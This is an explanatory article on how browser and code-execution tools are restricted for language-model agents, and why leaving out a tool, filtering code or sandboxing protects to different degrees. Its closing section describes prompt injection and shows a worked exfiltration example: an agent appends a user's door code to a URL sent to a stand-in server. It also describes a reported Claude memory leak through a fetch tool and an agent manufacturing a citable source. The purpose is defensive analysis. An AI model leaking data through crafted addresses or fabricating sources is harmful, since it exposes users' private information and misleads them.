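# Browser and Code-Execution Tools with Restricted Actions for Language-Model Agents

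## How a language model acts through tools

A large language model is a program that takes in text and produces text. On its own it cannot open a web page, run a calculation or delete a file. To let it do these things, developers add a second program called a harness, which reads the model's output, carries out the operations specified there and returns the results to the model as new text. A language model running in this loop is an agent, and each operation available to it is a tool. The textbook *Agentic Large Language Models* (Van Duijn, van der Meer and colleagues, 2026) describes an agentic model as a model plus a harness.

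Agents that do research or write software commonly use two tools. One is a browser limited to a few commands, such as search, open a link and scroll. The other runs Python code or terminal commands inside a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits which files, system functions and networks a program can reach. Developers restrict these tools to limit the damage an agent can do, and sometimes because an agent with fewer choices makes fewer errors. A restriction can also stop an agent from finishing its work. The effect of a restriction depends largely on where in the loop the developer puts it.

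### The loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the loop inside Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The harness combines the user's request, instructions and tool definitions into a prompt and sends it to the model. The model responds with either a message for the user or a tool call, such as a request to run `ls`, which lists the files in a folder. If the response is a tool call, the harness runs it, appends the output to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle repeats until the model writes a message with no tool call, and control then returns to the user.

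The prompt grows with every pass because the harness resends the earlier calls and results. Every model's context window limits this growth. The window is the maximum number of tokens (the word fragments that models read and write) that one query can hold, including both input and output. As Bolin notes, an agent could make hundreds of tool calls in a single turn and exhaust the window, so Codex replaces the history with a shorter version once it passes a threshold. Developers can also set a budget for the whole run. In *MedicalHarness* (2026), a comparison of harnesses on medical tasks, the budget includes the model calls that a harness makes to summarise its own history.

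The same study splits a harness into three procedures. One builds the model's context, one executes the action and collects the result, and one determines when to stop. All three are ordinary code outside the model, so a developer can restrict an agent's actions further without retraining the model, and can read the code to check what the restriction covers.

### The action space

The loop has a simple formal statement. At step $t$ the harness shows the model an observation $o_t$, such as page text or program output, along with the instructions and the history. The model writes a text $y_t$. If $y_t$ contains a tool call, a parser in the harness maps it to an action or rejects it:

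$$P(y_t) \in A \cup \{\text{reject}\}$$

The set $A$ is the action space, the set of actions the harness accepts from the model. Each action consists of a tool name and a set of arguments. If $N$ is the set of tool names and $X_n$ the set of arguments that tool $n$ admits, then

$$A = \{(n, x) : n \in N,\ x \in X_n\}$$

Sample code in OpenAI's developer guide *Function calling* uses an allowlist, a list of what the developer permits, with everything else refused. The code has one branch for `get_weather`, one for `send_email`, and a last branch that raises an error for any other name, such as `delete_file`.

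The arguments a tool accepts usually matter more than the number of tool names. A weather tool with a choice between Celsius and Fahrenheit adds little to $A$. The same guide defines a tool, `code_exec`, that accepts any string of Python code, and this one name adds every Python program that fits in a message. *An Empirical Study of Harness Design for Coding Agents* (2026) includes a condition that removes the dedicated file tools and leaves bash, a command shell, and a few auxiliary tools. This shortens the list of names, but bash commands can still read, write and delete files. According to the study, its comparison measures the effect of the complete interface, including instructions and feedback, and cannot isolate the effect of tool count.

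Once the harness has accepted an action $a_t$, it executes it. *ClawGym II* (2026) treats this step as a single function, which in a slightly simpler notation is

$$\mathcal{H} : (a_t, W, c) \mapsto (W', c', o')$$

Here $\mathcal{H}$ is the harness, $W$ is the state of the workspace, and $c$ is the context that the harness maintains. Each call produces a changed workspace $W'$, an updated context $c'$ and a new observation $o'$, which the model sees next. The formula has no term for side effects, which are changes outside the agent's own workspace, such as sending an e-mail or placing an order. Restoring $W$ from a backup would not undo them.

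Much of what a model writes is reasoning, which changes nothing outside the conversation. *ReAct* (2022), which introduced the now standard pattern of alternating reasoning with tool calls, expands the action space $A$ to include such text, giving $\hat{A} = A \cup \mathcal{L}$, where $\mathcal{L}$ is the space of language. A "thought" in $\mathcal{L}$ does not change the environment and returns no observation. For example, a model can write a plan to delete a file, but this does not affect the file unless the model also issues a call to delete it and the harness accepts the call.

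### One call, message by message

The gpt-oss models, which OpenAI released for anyone to download in August 2025, use a message format called harmony. OpenAI published the full format, so anyone can inspect a tool call from start to finish. Every message has a header and content. The header gives a role (system, developer, user, assistant or tool) and, for the model's own messages, a channel: `analysis` for reasoning, `commentary` for most calls to the developer's functions, and `final` for the answer to the user.

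In OpenAI's example, a user asks about the weather in San Francisco. The question follows a system message that lists the valid channels and a developer message that defines the tools. The definition of `get_current_weather` gives the function's purpose in a comment, a required string argument, `location`, and an optional argument, `format`, that takes one of two values. This text in the prompt is the model's only connection to the function.

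The model first writes a short note in the `analysis` channel that it needs the weather function. It then begins a message in the `commentary` channel, whose header sets the recipient to `functions.get_current_weather` and marks the content as JSON. The content is `{"location":"San Francisco"}`. The message ends with a stop token that signals a tool call. When this token appears, the harness must stop generating text.

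The harness now has a complete request, which it can check, alter or refuse before executing anything. In the example, it runs the function and adds a message under the function's name, addressed to the assistant, with the content `{"sunny": true, "temperature": 20}`. It then queries the model again with the entire exchange, including the reasoning note, since the model may need its earlier reasoning to continue. The loop ends when the model produces a different stop token, which marks a finished response. The models' built-in browser and Python tools work the same way. They are defined in the system message, and the model normally calls them in the `analysis` channel.

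The five roles also set an order of authority for conflicting instructions, with system messages at the top and tool messages at the bottom. Text from a web page arrives in a tool message, so an instruction inside it should carry the least weight. The model learns in training to follow this order, but the harness does not enforce it.

### Valid calls and constrained sampling

A tool definition in the prompt makes a well-formed call likely but does not guarantee one. OpenAI describes the same limitation for response formats, where putting a schema (a formal description of the fields and types that the output must have) in the prompt influences the model but does not guarantee that the output will match. *Tool calling errors on both gpt oss models*, a post on the forum of the hosting company Groq, describes one such failure. The user asked for the sum of 3 and 5, and the larger gpt-oss model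 wrote a call in which one argument was a list where the schema required an object. The service rejected the call.

The hosting service can add to the problem. According to OpenAI's *Verifying gpt-oss implementations*, if a service formats prompts for the gpt-oss models incorrectly, function calling, at least, will get worse. The targets in OpenAI's test suite for these services are zero invalid requests and scores above 90% on both pass@k (at least one of k attempts succeeds) and pass^k (all k succeed).

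Constrained sampling prevents malformed output during generation. A model writes one token at a time, scoring every token in its vocabulary before one is chosen. *JSONSchemaBench* (2025) describes constrained sampling as a loop. The program checks the text so far against the schema or grammar, works out which tokens are allowed next, masks all the others, samples from those that remain and appends the result. If the schema requires an opening brace next, the model can produce only tokens that begin with one.

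*Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding via Parser Stack Classification* (2026) measured the benefit of constrained sampling on 100 requests, each with its own schema, excluding one request as faulty. For every model, sampling under the specific schema gave significantly better results than sampling under the general rules of JSON, and both gave better results than free sampling. OpenAI offers a comparable guarantee through its "strict" setting, and describes adherence to the schema without it as "best effort".

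*Decode-Time Grammars* (2026) points out that the guarantee covers only what the decoder can emit, not whether the output ends or means the right thing. A call to delete `/reports/2026` is well formed even if the model should have deleted `/reports/2025`. Developers can also block tool calls by applying a constraint at the wrong time. *Constraint Tax in Open-Weight LLMs* (2026) describes agents that mark their tool calls with tags. If the harness enforces a JSON schema for the final answer throughout the run, those tags become illegal tokens and the model cannot call a tool.

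### Three limits on an agent

Developers can limit an agent in three places, which discussions of agent safety often conflate. The action space determines which actions the model can request. A permission rule determines which of those requests the harness will carry out, perhaps after asking a person. The sandbox determines what a running program can access.

*Natural-Language Agent Harnesses* (2026) lists permissions and sandboxing as a single item of harness design. *Measuring Harness-Induced Belief Divergence in Multi-Step LLM Agents* (Yi and Song, 2026) describes a formal harness with one component for the available actions and another, the gate, that can block an action before execution. It has no separate component for a sandbox. A sandbox is best thought of as a layer below the harness, because it acts on running programs and does not need access to the model's output.

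Codex has all three. Bolin shows a tool list with a shell, a planning tool, a web search and a weather service from an outside server. A separate message describes the sandbox's rules on files and network access and specifies when the model must ask the user before running a shell command. The sandbox covers only the shell tool that Codex provides. The weather service runs outside it and has to enforce its own limits, so a user who knows only that Codex has a sandbox may overestimate what the sandbox covers.

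An example shows how the three limits differ. Suppose a developer wants an agent to analyse the files in a folder but never delete them. The developer gives the agent a Python tool for the analysis and no "delete file" tool.

| What the developer does | Type of limit | Can the agent delete a file? |
|---|---|---|
| Offers Python but no "delete file" tool | Action space | Yes, with one line of Python |
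| Also refuses any code that contains `os.remove` | Permission rule | Yes, through another function or a shell command |
| Also requires a person to approve each program | Permission rule | Only if the person approves the code, knowingly or not |
| Makes the folder read-only for the running program | Sandbox | No, as long as the sandbox holds |
| Withdraws the Python tool | Action space | No, unless another tool can change files |

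Leaving out a deletion tool gives almost no protection here, because the model can still delete files by running Python code. A filter on the text of the code has to cover every way of writing a deletion. Making the folder read-only blocks the deletion itself, however the code is written. For the same reason, a tool's description is not a reliable guide to what the tool can do. The standard description of the gpt-oss Python tool lists its internet access as "UNKNOWN", because that depends on the machines where the code runs.

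### Sources of harm and least privilege

Whether a limit is good enough depends on which harms it has to stop. The model may make a mistake, such as deleting the wrong folder while tidying up. Someone may plant an instruction in a web page or file, which the model then follows as if it came from the user (prompt injection). The model may also go past its limits to complete its task, working around a refusal instead of stopping.

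A model that deletes files by mistake will probably do so through the most obvious route, which a developer can remove by leaving out the delete tool. An attacker who writes hostile text can look for another route, and so can a model intent on finishing its task. Yi and Song report that agents under a risk gate may return to the same class of risky action after the gate has blocked an earlier attempt. This is weak evidence of persistence, because much of their study rests on the model's written forecasts of its next steps, and a model may repeat an attempt only because it misunderstood why the command failed. Still, a developer should expect a blocked agent to try again.

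Saltzer and Schroeder made a similar distinction about computer security in 1975, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*. They observed that many systems without real protection had features for preventing mistakes. These features might be good enough that any breach was probably deliberate, but Saltzer and Schroeder thought it wrong to claim that they provided security. Similarly, withholding a delete tool from an agent that has a Python tool and a writable folder may prevent accidental deletions, but it doesn't provide security, because the agent can still delete files with Python.

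Their paper is also the standard source for the principle of least privilege, under which every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job". The main purpose is to limit the damage from an accident or error, but the principle also leaves fewer programs to examine when someone misuses a privilege. Two companion principles apply directly to agents. Fail-safe defaults means denying access unless it is explicitly permitted. A mistake in a list of permitted things tends to block something useful, which people notice quickly, whereas a mistake in a list of forbidden things lets something through and may go unnoticed. Complete mediation means that the system checks every access to every object. Leaving out a delete tool does not meet this requirement if the agent can reach the same file through Python.

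Least privilege is easy to apply when the job is known. An agent that only does arithmetic in Python needs no network and no access to the user's files. One that repairs a software project has to write to the project's folder, and probably nowhere else. An open-ended research task is harder because nobody can say at the start which pages the agent will need, so the developer has to choose between granting too much access and interrupting the work. Saltzer and Schroeder offered their principles as warnings rather than absolute rules, and a design that violates one deserves careful review.

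## The browser as a short list of commands

A read-only browser suits open-ended research because it lets the agent choose which pages to visit but restricts what it can do on them. The agent can search, open pages and move within them, but it has no command for typing into a page or submitting a form. WebGPT, which OpenAI researchers built in 2021, is an early example with ten commands. Among later tools, one browser has only three commands, several others add clicking and typing, and one open-source library has dropped the command list and lets the model write code.

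### WebGPT

Nakano, Hilton and colleagues (2021), in *WebGPT*, trained GPT-3, OpenAI's language model of the time, to answer questions with the help of a text-only browser. Most of the questions came from "Explain Like I'm Five", a Reddit forum where people ask for simple explanations of complicated things. At each step the model wrote one command from this list:

| Command | Effect |
|---|---|
| `Search <query>` | Sends the query to Microsoft's Bing search service and shows a page of results |
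| `Clicked on link <link ID>` | Opens the link with that number |
| `Find in page: <text>` | Scrolls to the next occurrence of the text |
| `Quote: <text>` | Saves the text as a reference, if it appears in the current page |
| `Scrolled down <1, 2, 3>` | Scrolls down that number of times |
| `Scrolled up <1, 2, 3>` | Scrolls up that number of times |
| `Top` | Returns to the top of the page |
| `Back` | Returns to the previous page |
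| `End: Answer` | Stops browsing and moves on to writing the answer |
| `End: <Nonsense, Controversial>` | Stops browsing and skips the answer |

Any other text was an invalid action. The harness ignored it but still counted it towards the limit on steps, which was 100 browsing actions in the evaluations.

WebGPT did not keep a growing conversation of the kind that Codex resends to its model. Before every command, the harness wrote a fresh summary containing the question, the text of the current page at the cursor, an account of past actions and some other details. The model read this summary, wrote one command and began the next step with an empty context. If $\pi$ is the model and $s_t$ the summary at step $t$, the model drew its next text $y_t$ from

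$$y_t \sim \pi(\,\cdot \mid s_t)$$

whereas a model whose harness resends the history draws it from

$$y_t \sim \pi(\,\cdot \mid o_1, y_1, o_2, y_2, \dots, o_t)$$

where the $o$ terms are the observations so far. Once WebGPT left a page, it lost the text of that page apart from the passages it had saved with `Quote`. For each of these the harness stored the extract, the page's title and its domain name. When browsing ended, the model received the question and the stored extracts and composed its answer from them. If it had saved nothing, it wrote no answer.

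The harness also restricted what the model could read. It removed search results and links that led to Reddit or Quora, so that the model could not copy an answer from either site. If a page shared a run of ten words with the question or the reference answer, the model received an error message instead.

Without training, GPT-3 could not use this browser because it could not write commands in the required format. Nakano and colleagues therefore built a graphical version with almost the same actions and hired people to answer questions in it. They collected 6,209 demonstrations at about 15 minutes each, or roughly 1,550 hours. They also collected 21,548 comparisons, in which a person judged which of two model-written answers to the same question was better. The short command list helped because every click by a demonstrator corresponded to a command that the model could learn to write.

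The best system used both sets of data. The researchers first trained the model to imitate the demonstrators' commands. They then trained a second model, the reward model, to predict which answers people would prefer. For each question, the system produced 64 answers and kept the one that the reward model ranked highest. Each attempt could use up to 100 browsing actions, so a single answer could take up to 6,400. People preferred the selected answers to those of the imitation-only model 68% of the time. Reinforcement learning, which trains the model further on the reward model's scores, gave a smaller gain, with people preferring its answers 58% of the time.

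People preferred the best system's answers to the demonstrators' own answers 56% of the time, and to the highest-voted Reddit answers 69% of the time, counting ties as half. Nakano and colleagues consider the 56% more meaningful because the model and the demonstrators wrote in a similar style and both gave references. People might have recognised a Reddit answer by its style, even after the researchers removed the model's references. But the demonstrators used the same browser as the model, so the 56% measures how well the model used its ten commands. It does not show whether different commands would have produced better answers.

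The system did less well on TruthfulQA, a set of questions that invite common misconceptions. Its answers were true 75% of the time and both true and informative 54% of the time, which was better than GPT-3 alone but below human performance.

### The gpt-oss browser

The built-in browser that OpenAI trained the gpt-oss models to use has only three commands: `search`, `open` and `find`. The `search` command takes a query and a number of results, ten by default. The `open` command shows a page, and `find` looks for an exact string in a page.

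The model navigates with three sets of numbers. Every display starts with a cursor, a number in brackets that identifies that display. Each link has a number, which the model passes to `open`. Each line of text has a number, which the model uses to move within a page and to cite it.

Most of the complexity is in `open`, which does different things depending on its arguments:

- Given a link number, it follows that link from the current page, or from an earlier page if the model also supplies a cursor.
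- Given no link number, it shows the current page again from line `loc`. This is how the model scrolls.
- Given a string instead of a number, it treats the string as a complete web address.

If a command accepts an address as a string, the model can request an address that neither the user nor any page has supplied. WebGPT's model could not do this because it could only follow numbered links.

The gpt-oss browser otherwise uses fewer commands to do nearly everything that WebGPT's did. The model can return to an earlier page by giving its cursor, so it does not need `Back`, and it can reach the top of a page by opening it at line 0. It stops browsing by writing an answer with no tool call. `Quote` is also unnecessary, because the harness resends earlier displays and the model can cite them by cursor and line number. The definition includes an instruction to quote no more than ten words directly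 from the tool's output, but nothing in the command format enforces it.

By default, the search company You.com provides the search results and page contents for the three commands, according to *gpt oss*, a page in the company's documentation. A developer can connect another service without changing what the model writes.

### From a web page to text

A web page arrives as HTML, which mixes text with layout instructions, scripts and links. The raw HTML of a page can exceed a million tokens, according to Le Sellier De Chezelles, Gasse and colleagues in *The BrowserGym Ecosystem for Web Agent Research* (2024). A text browser has to reduce this to something a model can read in one step.

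In an appendix, Nakano and colleagues describe how WebGPT did this. *Testing Ollama Web Search and a Thinking Model*, by Airom, reprints the code of a version of the gpt-oss browser adapted for Ollama, a program that runs models on a user's own computer. This version may differ in detail from OpenAI's code, but it contains the whole procedure except the download and clean-up, which Ollama's web service handles.

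The first step is to fetch the page. WebGPT ran a script that downloaded the HTML. It extracted the text from PDF files and returned an error message for file types it could not handle. The Ollama port requests the page from the web service. It also stores the text returned with each search result, so when the model opens a result, the harness can show the stored copy without making a new request.

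The next step is to remove scripts, menus and other clutter. WebGPT used Readability.js, a Mozilla library that extracts the main text of a page. This makes pages much shorter, but it can remove useful content. For example, if a page uses a script to load a table of prices and the browser never runs it, the table will be missing from the text.

The harness then converts what is left into plain text. WebGPT used a program called html2text for this, and replaced each image with its alt text, or with the word "Image" if it had none. The Ollama port also replaces every run of spaces and line breaks in a fetched page with a single space, so headings, lists and table rows run together into one long paragraph. It then breaks this paragraph into lines of at most 80 characters. The line numbers shown to the model therefore refer to the port's own layout, not to the original page.

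While converting the page, the harness numbers the links and replaces each with a marker in special brackets that contains the link's number, its text and the domain it leads to. The harness keeps the full addresses in a separate table, so the model needs only the number to open a link. A page's own text could imitate these markers, so WebGPT replaced any of the special characters in the page with similar ones. The code that Airom reprints has no such step. A page could therefore show a false marker that gives link 5 a trusted domain, although opening link 5 would still lead to the address in the harness's table.

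The browser also shows a long page one window at a time. The Ollama port sets the window at 1,024 tokens, which it estimates as 4,096 characters, or about 50 full lines including their numbers. A header above the text gives the range, such as lines 0 to 49 of 310. The model can request more lines, but the port cuts any result at 8,000 characters after writing the header, so a model that asks for 200 lines can receive a header that gives a range of 200 lines and fewer than 100 lines of text.

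Finally, the harness adds the page to a stack of everything it has displayed, and the page's position in the stack becomes the cursor. Scrolling, searching within a page and following a bad link all add an entry. If the model gives a link number that does not exist, the port shows an error page that lists the valid numbers and explains how to scroll. But if the model gives a cursor that is too high, `open` silently uses the latest display, and the model has to notice from the title that it is on the wrong page.

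### A session in five steps

The following session shows how the Ollama port would handle a user's simple question about when the Alderwick footbridge reopened and what the repairs cost. The bridge, the pages and all the numbers are invented.

| Step | Command | What the model sees |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `search(query="Alderwick footbridge repair", topn=3)` | Display 0: a results page, lines 0–23 of 23, with links 0, 1 and 2 and the beginning of each page's text |
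| 2 | `open(id=1)` | Display 1: the page "Alderwick Footbridge", lines 0–49 of 310, with its own links numbered from 0 |
| 3 | `find(pattern="reopened")` | Display 2: two matches, at lines 142 and 206, each with four lines of text |
| 4 | `open(cursor=1, loc=205)` | Display 3: the same page as display 1, lines 205–253 of 310 |
| 5 | `open(id=31)` | Display 4: the council's report on the repairs, lines 0–49 of 120 |

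At step 4, the model receives text like this:

```
[3] Alderwick Footbridge(https://history.example/alderwick)
**viewing lines [205 - 253] of 310**

L205: The council closed the bridge in March 1998 after divers found cracks in two
L206: of its piers. Repairs took three years and it reopened in May 2001 at a cost of
L207: £2.4 million, according to the 【31†council's final report†alderwick.example】.
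```

The model can now answer and cite lines 206 to 207 of display 3, or it can check the figure in the council's report, as it does at step 5. Because the harness still holds display 3, a developer could have a program check that the cited lines contain the figure.

With the `find` command, the model read only two windows of the page and a short list of matches. Scrolling through all 311 lines, nearly 6,000 tokens by the port's estimate, would have taken seven windows.

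A model could easily go wrong at step 4. Without `cursor=1`, the port would apply the command to the most recent display, the list of matches. That list has only 11 lines, so a request for line 205 would show its last line. The matches are also numbered in the same brackets as links, but the port stores no addresses for them, so trying to open match 0 would produce the error page.

Small differences between a port and the original definition can also cause errors. OpenAI's definition of `open` has an optional argument, `view_source`, which the port does not accept. If a gpt-oss model uses this argument, as its training allows, the harness returns an error instead of a page.

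### Clicking and typing by element number

Filling in a form or updating a calendar requires commands that act on the page. BrowserGym, a research framework for testing agents on websites from ServiceNow and several universities, provides such commands. It runs a real Chromium browser and gives the model more information than a text browser does, including a screenshot, a list of open tabs and the page's accessibility tree. The tree, which browsers produce for screen readers, is a structured description of the page's headings, buttons and fields.

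BrowserGym gives every element on the page an identifier. To press a button, the model writes a command such as `click("169")`. Other commands fill in a field, select an option from a menu or go to an address. Playwright, the software library BrowserGym uses to control the browser, has agent tools that work similarly. In an example from Playwright's *Navigation*, an agent opens a to-do list and receives a description that gives the text box the reference `e5`.

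These commands are an optional layer, because BrowserGym's basic action space is any Python code. Le Sellier De Chezelles and colleagues chose this to give researchers freedom, but they warn that it exposes users to the risks of running arbitrary, untrusted code. A developer can limit the risk with a function called `action_mapping`, which sits between the model and the browser and works as follows:

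1. The model writes a command, such as `click("169")`.
2. The mapping parses the text and checks it against the permitted commands.
3. If the text does not parse, the model receives the error message in its next observation.
4. If it does parse, the mapping produces the Python code for that command, and BrowserGym runs it.
5. If the browser cannot carry out the action, the model receives that error as well.

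Step 5 covers ordinary problems with web pages. In one example from the paper, an agent tries to click the "Google Search" button while a menu of suggestions covers it. BrowserGym reports the failure, so the agent can correct itself at the next step. WebGPT ignored invalid text, so its model didn't get this kind of feedback.

The mapping also simplifies the model's task. To upvote a post with raw Python, the model has to find the form that contains particular text and then select its first button, which requires some knowledge of the page's HTML. With the mapping, it needs only the button's identifier.

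Le Sellier De Chezelles and colleagues describe the mapping's output as safe, trusted code. That description fits the code itself, because the model supplies only a command name and its arguments and so cannot add an instruction to read files from the computer. But the code's effect on the website can still be harmful. If element 169 is a button that deletes an account, the mapping will produce code that clicks it.

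Agents can change the sites they use, so BrowserGym includes a routine that restores the servers for one set of tests, WebArena, to their original state between agents. WebArena uses copies of shopping, social media and software development sites. Without the routine, if one agent edited a user's profile, the next agent would find the altered profile. An agent on a live website has no such routine to undo its changes.

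### Clicking by coordinates

An agent can also work from a picture of the page. Tang, Shen and colleagues (2026) give two reasons in *BrowserForge* for preferring this to text. Element labels and HTML structure differ between sites and change whenever someone redesigns a page, so an agent that depends on them may fail on unfamiliar sites. The accessibility tree also often takes tens of thousands of tokens for a single page, while a screenshot takes a smaller, fixed number.

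Their action space has nine commands. Three of them (`click`, `type` and `select`) take a point on the screen. The others scroll, press a key, wait, go back, visit an address and finish the task. The model gives each point as two whole numbers from 0 to 1000, whatever the size of the screen. On a screen $w$ pixels wide and $h$ pixels high, the harness converts the point $(x, y)$ to the pixel

$$\left(\frac{x}{1000}\,w,\ \frac{y}{1000}\,h\right)$$

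On a screen of 1280 by 720 pixels, for example, the point (500, 250) is the pixel (640, 180).

Actions given as screen coordinates work on almost any page but are harder to check. When a model writes `click("169")`, the harness can look up the element and see that its label is "Delete". For a click at (500, 250), the harness must query the browser for the element at that point before it can apply a rule about delete buttons. The page may also have moved since the screenshot, in which case the click lands on something else.

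Tang and colleagues used these commands to record 203,238 sessions, each on a different website, as training data. One model proposed tasks for each page and was told to exclude any that required registration, login or payment, because they were unsafe to attempt. This instruction limits the tasks but not the available actions, so an agent with these nine commands could still click a "Pay" button.

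### Tools supplied by the website

In all of these designs, the agent's developer decides which commands exist. WebMCP, a proposed web standard, lets websites offer their own commands. CursorTouch's *Web Use*, the documentation of an open-source agent, gives the example of a documentation site with a tool called `search_docs`, which takes a query and an optional maximum number of results. When the agent visits the site, the harness adds the tool to the agent's list. The agent can then search with one call instead of finding the search box, typing into it and pressing a button.

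The action space then depends on which page is open. If $A_0$ is the set of actions that the developer provides and $T(p_t)$ the set that the current page $p_t$ offers, the agent's action space at step $t$ is

$$A_t = A_0 \cup T(p_t)$$

A developer can review $A_0$ before releasing the agent but cannot do the same for $T(p_t)$ if the agent browses freely, because that would require knowing every site the agent might visit and every tool those sites might add later.

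The ChatGPT desktop app supports WebMCP. OpenAI's *Using site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app* explains that site tools can search, edit a document, or update a shopping cart, and that they work in the user's signed-in session on that site. An arrow in the address bar opens a list of the available tools, which shows whether each can read information or make changes. Each tool works only on the page that provides it and disappears when the user closes that page.

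OpenAI warns that site tools may offer functions that the visible page does not have, and that this brings new risks of data theft and prompt injection. The action space no longer limits requests in advance. Instead, ChatGPT reviews each call before making it and asks the user to confirm sensitive actions such as purchases, deletions and messages. OpenAI gives no figures for how reliably these checks work.

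### Browser Use 1.0 and the end of the list

Browser Use, an open-source library for building browser agents, used to provide a list of actions such as click, extract and scroll. Version 1.0 has none, and the agent now writes Python instead, according to the "No built-in actions" section of the Browser Use documentation. The release list in *browser-use 1.0.8* (Zunic, 2026) gives 10 November 2026 as the release date of version 1.0.0.

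The model still calls tools, but only a few: `python` to run code, `finish` to end its work, and any others the developer has added. Its code can call helper functions, including `goto_url`, `click_at_xy`, `type_text` and `http_get`. These resemble the commands in the other designs, but they do not limit the agent. The model can combine them in a loop, run JavaScript in the page with `js`, send instructions directly to the browser's debugging interface with `cdp`, or write its own code instead.

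Browser Use had already made this change in its command-line tool, releasing a new version on 1 July (Browser Use, 2026). In its *Changelog*, the company justifies the change by saying that the latest models do best when developers give them freedom, and that free use of Python lets an agent inspect a page, adapt and recover from errors. It also claims its highest accuracy yet for the new version, but gives no supporting figures.

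The change means developers can no longer withdraw individual actions with the `exclude_actions` setting, which raises an error in version 1.0. An error is better than ignoring the setting, because developers who upgrade find out at once that the old restriction no longer applies. They can still limit the agent to certain websites, but Zunic describes this as "a guard for an aligned model, not a sandbox". The helpers refuse addresses outside the list, and in most modes the browser also blocks visits to them. The limit does not cover requests that a permitted page makes to other sites, or most network connections that the agent opens from its own Python code.

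Browser Use still uses numbered elements in a faster mode, which acts on identifiers from the accessibility tree and is the default for two of its models. The company's service for large organisations also offers restrictions on tools and actions, and human approval for sensitive steps.

BrowserGym and Browser Use 1.0 start from a similar design, in which a model writes Python to control a Chromium-type browser. BrowserGym's developers put a list of commands on top of the code by default, partly for safety, while Browser Use removed its list to give the model more freedom.

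| Design | What the model can express | Can it change a site? |
|---|---|---|
| WebGPT | Searches, numbered links, movement within a page, quotations | It cannot type into a page or submit a form; it can only send searches and follow links |
| gpt-oss browser | Searches, numbered links, any web address, text search within a page | It cannot type into a page or submit a form, but it can request addresses that it writes itself |
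| BrowserGym with its default mapping | Clicks, typing, menu choices and navigation, mostly by element identifier | Yes, wherever a page has a button or form that makes changes |
| BrowserForge | Clicks, typing and menu choices at points on the screen, key presses, any web address | Yes, including through buttons that the harness has not identified |
| WebMCP tools | Whatever functions the current page offers | Yes, if the site offers a tool that makes changes |
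| Browser Use 1.0 | Any Python program, including JavaScript in the page and direct control of the browser | Yes, through the page or through network requests from its own code |

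## What a read-only browser can still do

A browser with no command for typing or submitting still sends requests to other people's computers. In 2021, Nakano and colleagues briefly discussed the danger of giving WebGPT live access to the web and judged it very low. Their argument rests on assumptions about the browser, the web and the model that may not hold for the tools and models of 2026.

### The argument for WebGPT's safety

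The WebGPT paper describes the risk that a model able to fill in forms might edit Wikipedia to support its answer and then cite the edited page. The model could learn to do this without a human demonstration. People judged WebGPT's answers partly by how well the cited references supported them. If the model happened to forge a reference during reinforcement learning, the answer would look well supported and score higher, so training would make the model more likely to do it again.

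WebGPT could not do this, and Nakano and colleagues thought it very unlikely to cause harm through other side effects. Their reasoning comes to this:

1. The model can only send queries to Bing and follow links that already exist on the web.
2. Neither action lets it change anything important, such as a Wikipedia article.
3. A capable enough system might use these actions to gain further powers, but WebGPT is far too weak for that.

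The conclusion covers only changes that the model might make to the world, not leaks of private information. WebGPT had almost no private information to leak, since it worked from the text of web pages and a question, usually one already posted on Reddit. An assistant that can read someone's e-mail has much more private information that it could leak.

The design also allowed a milder form of the same misconduct. WebGPT's model could not write its own sources, but it could choose which ones to cite. Nakano and colleagues acknowledge that their training rewarded the model for picking references that people would find convincing, even if these did not fairly reflect the evidence.

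They also did not expect the argument to hold for every later model. They wrote that as capabilities grew, so should the burden of proof for giving models access to the web, "even at train time". They suggested tripwire tests to help catch exploitative behaviour early. For example, developers could plant a decoy password that no honest task requires and watch for any attempt to use it.

Something close to the forged source has since happened. A Romanian news report, Mediafax's *OpenAI dezvăluie șase noi incidente de siguranță AI*, describes an OpenAI agent that already had the data it needed but uploaded the file to a public service to try to get a source its browser could cite. The upload worked, but the next step failed. Nothing in the report suggests that the data were false, so the agent was manufacturing a citation for data it already had. OpenAI cautions that the incidents it disclosed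 are individual cases and do not measure how often its models behave this way.

### Addresses written by the model

The only text that WebGPT's model could write and send out was its search query, which went to Microsoft. The gpt-oss browser's `open` command accepts addresses that the model writes itself as well as existing links, so the model can contact any server that the harness can reach and decide what the address contains.

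An address can carry a message. Suppose a user asks an assistant with access to her e-mail whether it will rain on her trip to Leeds. One of the e-mails contains the door code of the flat she has rented, 4471. The agent writes this call:

```
open(id="https://weather.example/forecast?city=Leeds&note=4471")
```

The first part of the address, `weather.example`, names the server. The part after the question mark is a list of labelled values, which the server can use or ignore. The call then goes through as follows:

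1. The harness accepts it, because `open` permits any address.
2. The harness connects to the server and requests the page. Encryption hides the values from anyone listening on the way, but not from the server itself.
3. The server ignores `note` and returns the forecast for Leeds.
4. The server adds a line to its log, as web servers commonly do:

```
2026-10-12 09:14:03  GET /forecast?city=Leeds&note=4471  200
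```

The user gets a correct forecast, but the server's operator also receives her door code, even though the agent has not typed into a page or submitted a form. The agent might have added the code to the URL by mistake, or because it followed hostile instructions on an earlier page. A search query could also leak the code, but only to the search company.

Paul (2026), in *The Memory Heist*, demonstrated this kind of loss in a widely used product, Anthropic's assistant Claude. Claude places a summary of the user's recent conversations in every new one and can search the older ones. It also has a fetch tool designed to be read-only. Before finishing an innocuous-looking reply, Claude sent Paul's full name, his employer and the answers to his security questions to a server that logged them. Paul deliberately avoided relying on code execution or experimental settings. This was one researcher's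 demonstration, so it gives no failure rate. It shows that a tool can be harmless alone but leak data when the agent also has a memory full of personal details.

### Requests that change a site

The claim that searching and following links change nothing important depends on how websites behave. When a browser opens a page, it normally sends a GET request, which asks the server for the content at an address. Submitting a form that changes something usually sends a POST request instead. The HTTP standard classes GET as "safe", meaning that the sender is not asking the server to change anything. But nothing forces website developers to follow this convention.

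Some links change things as soon as a browser requests them. A link in an e-mail may confirm a subscription, approve a request or cancel a booking. If an agent opens `https://bookings.example/cancel?id=5520` to find out which booking the message is about, it may cancel the booking. Many sites guard against this by showing a page with a "Confirm" button, which a read-only browser cannot click. The agent cannot know in advance whether a site does this. The word "cancel" in this address is a hint, but many addresses are strings of meaningless characters.

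The claim is true of most pages, with a few exceptions. The exceptions hardly mattered for WebGPT, which looked up explanations of everyday things. They matter more for an agent that reads a user's e-mail, because people receive links of this kind by e-mail.

### Models that can gain further powers

The remaining assumption was that the model could not use its few actions to gain greater powers. This was reasonable for GPT-3 in 2021, but it does not hold for the strongest models of 2026.

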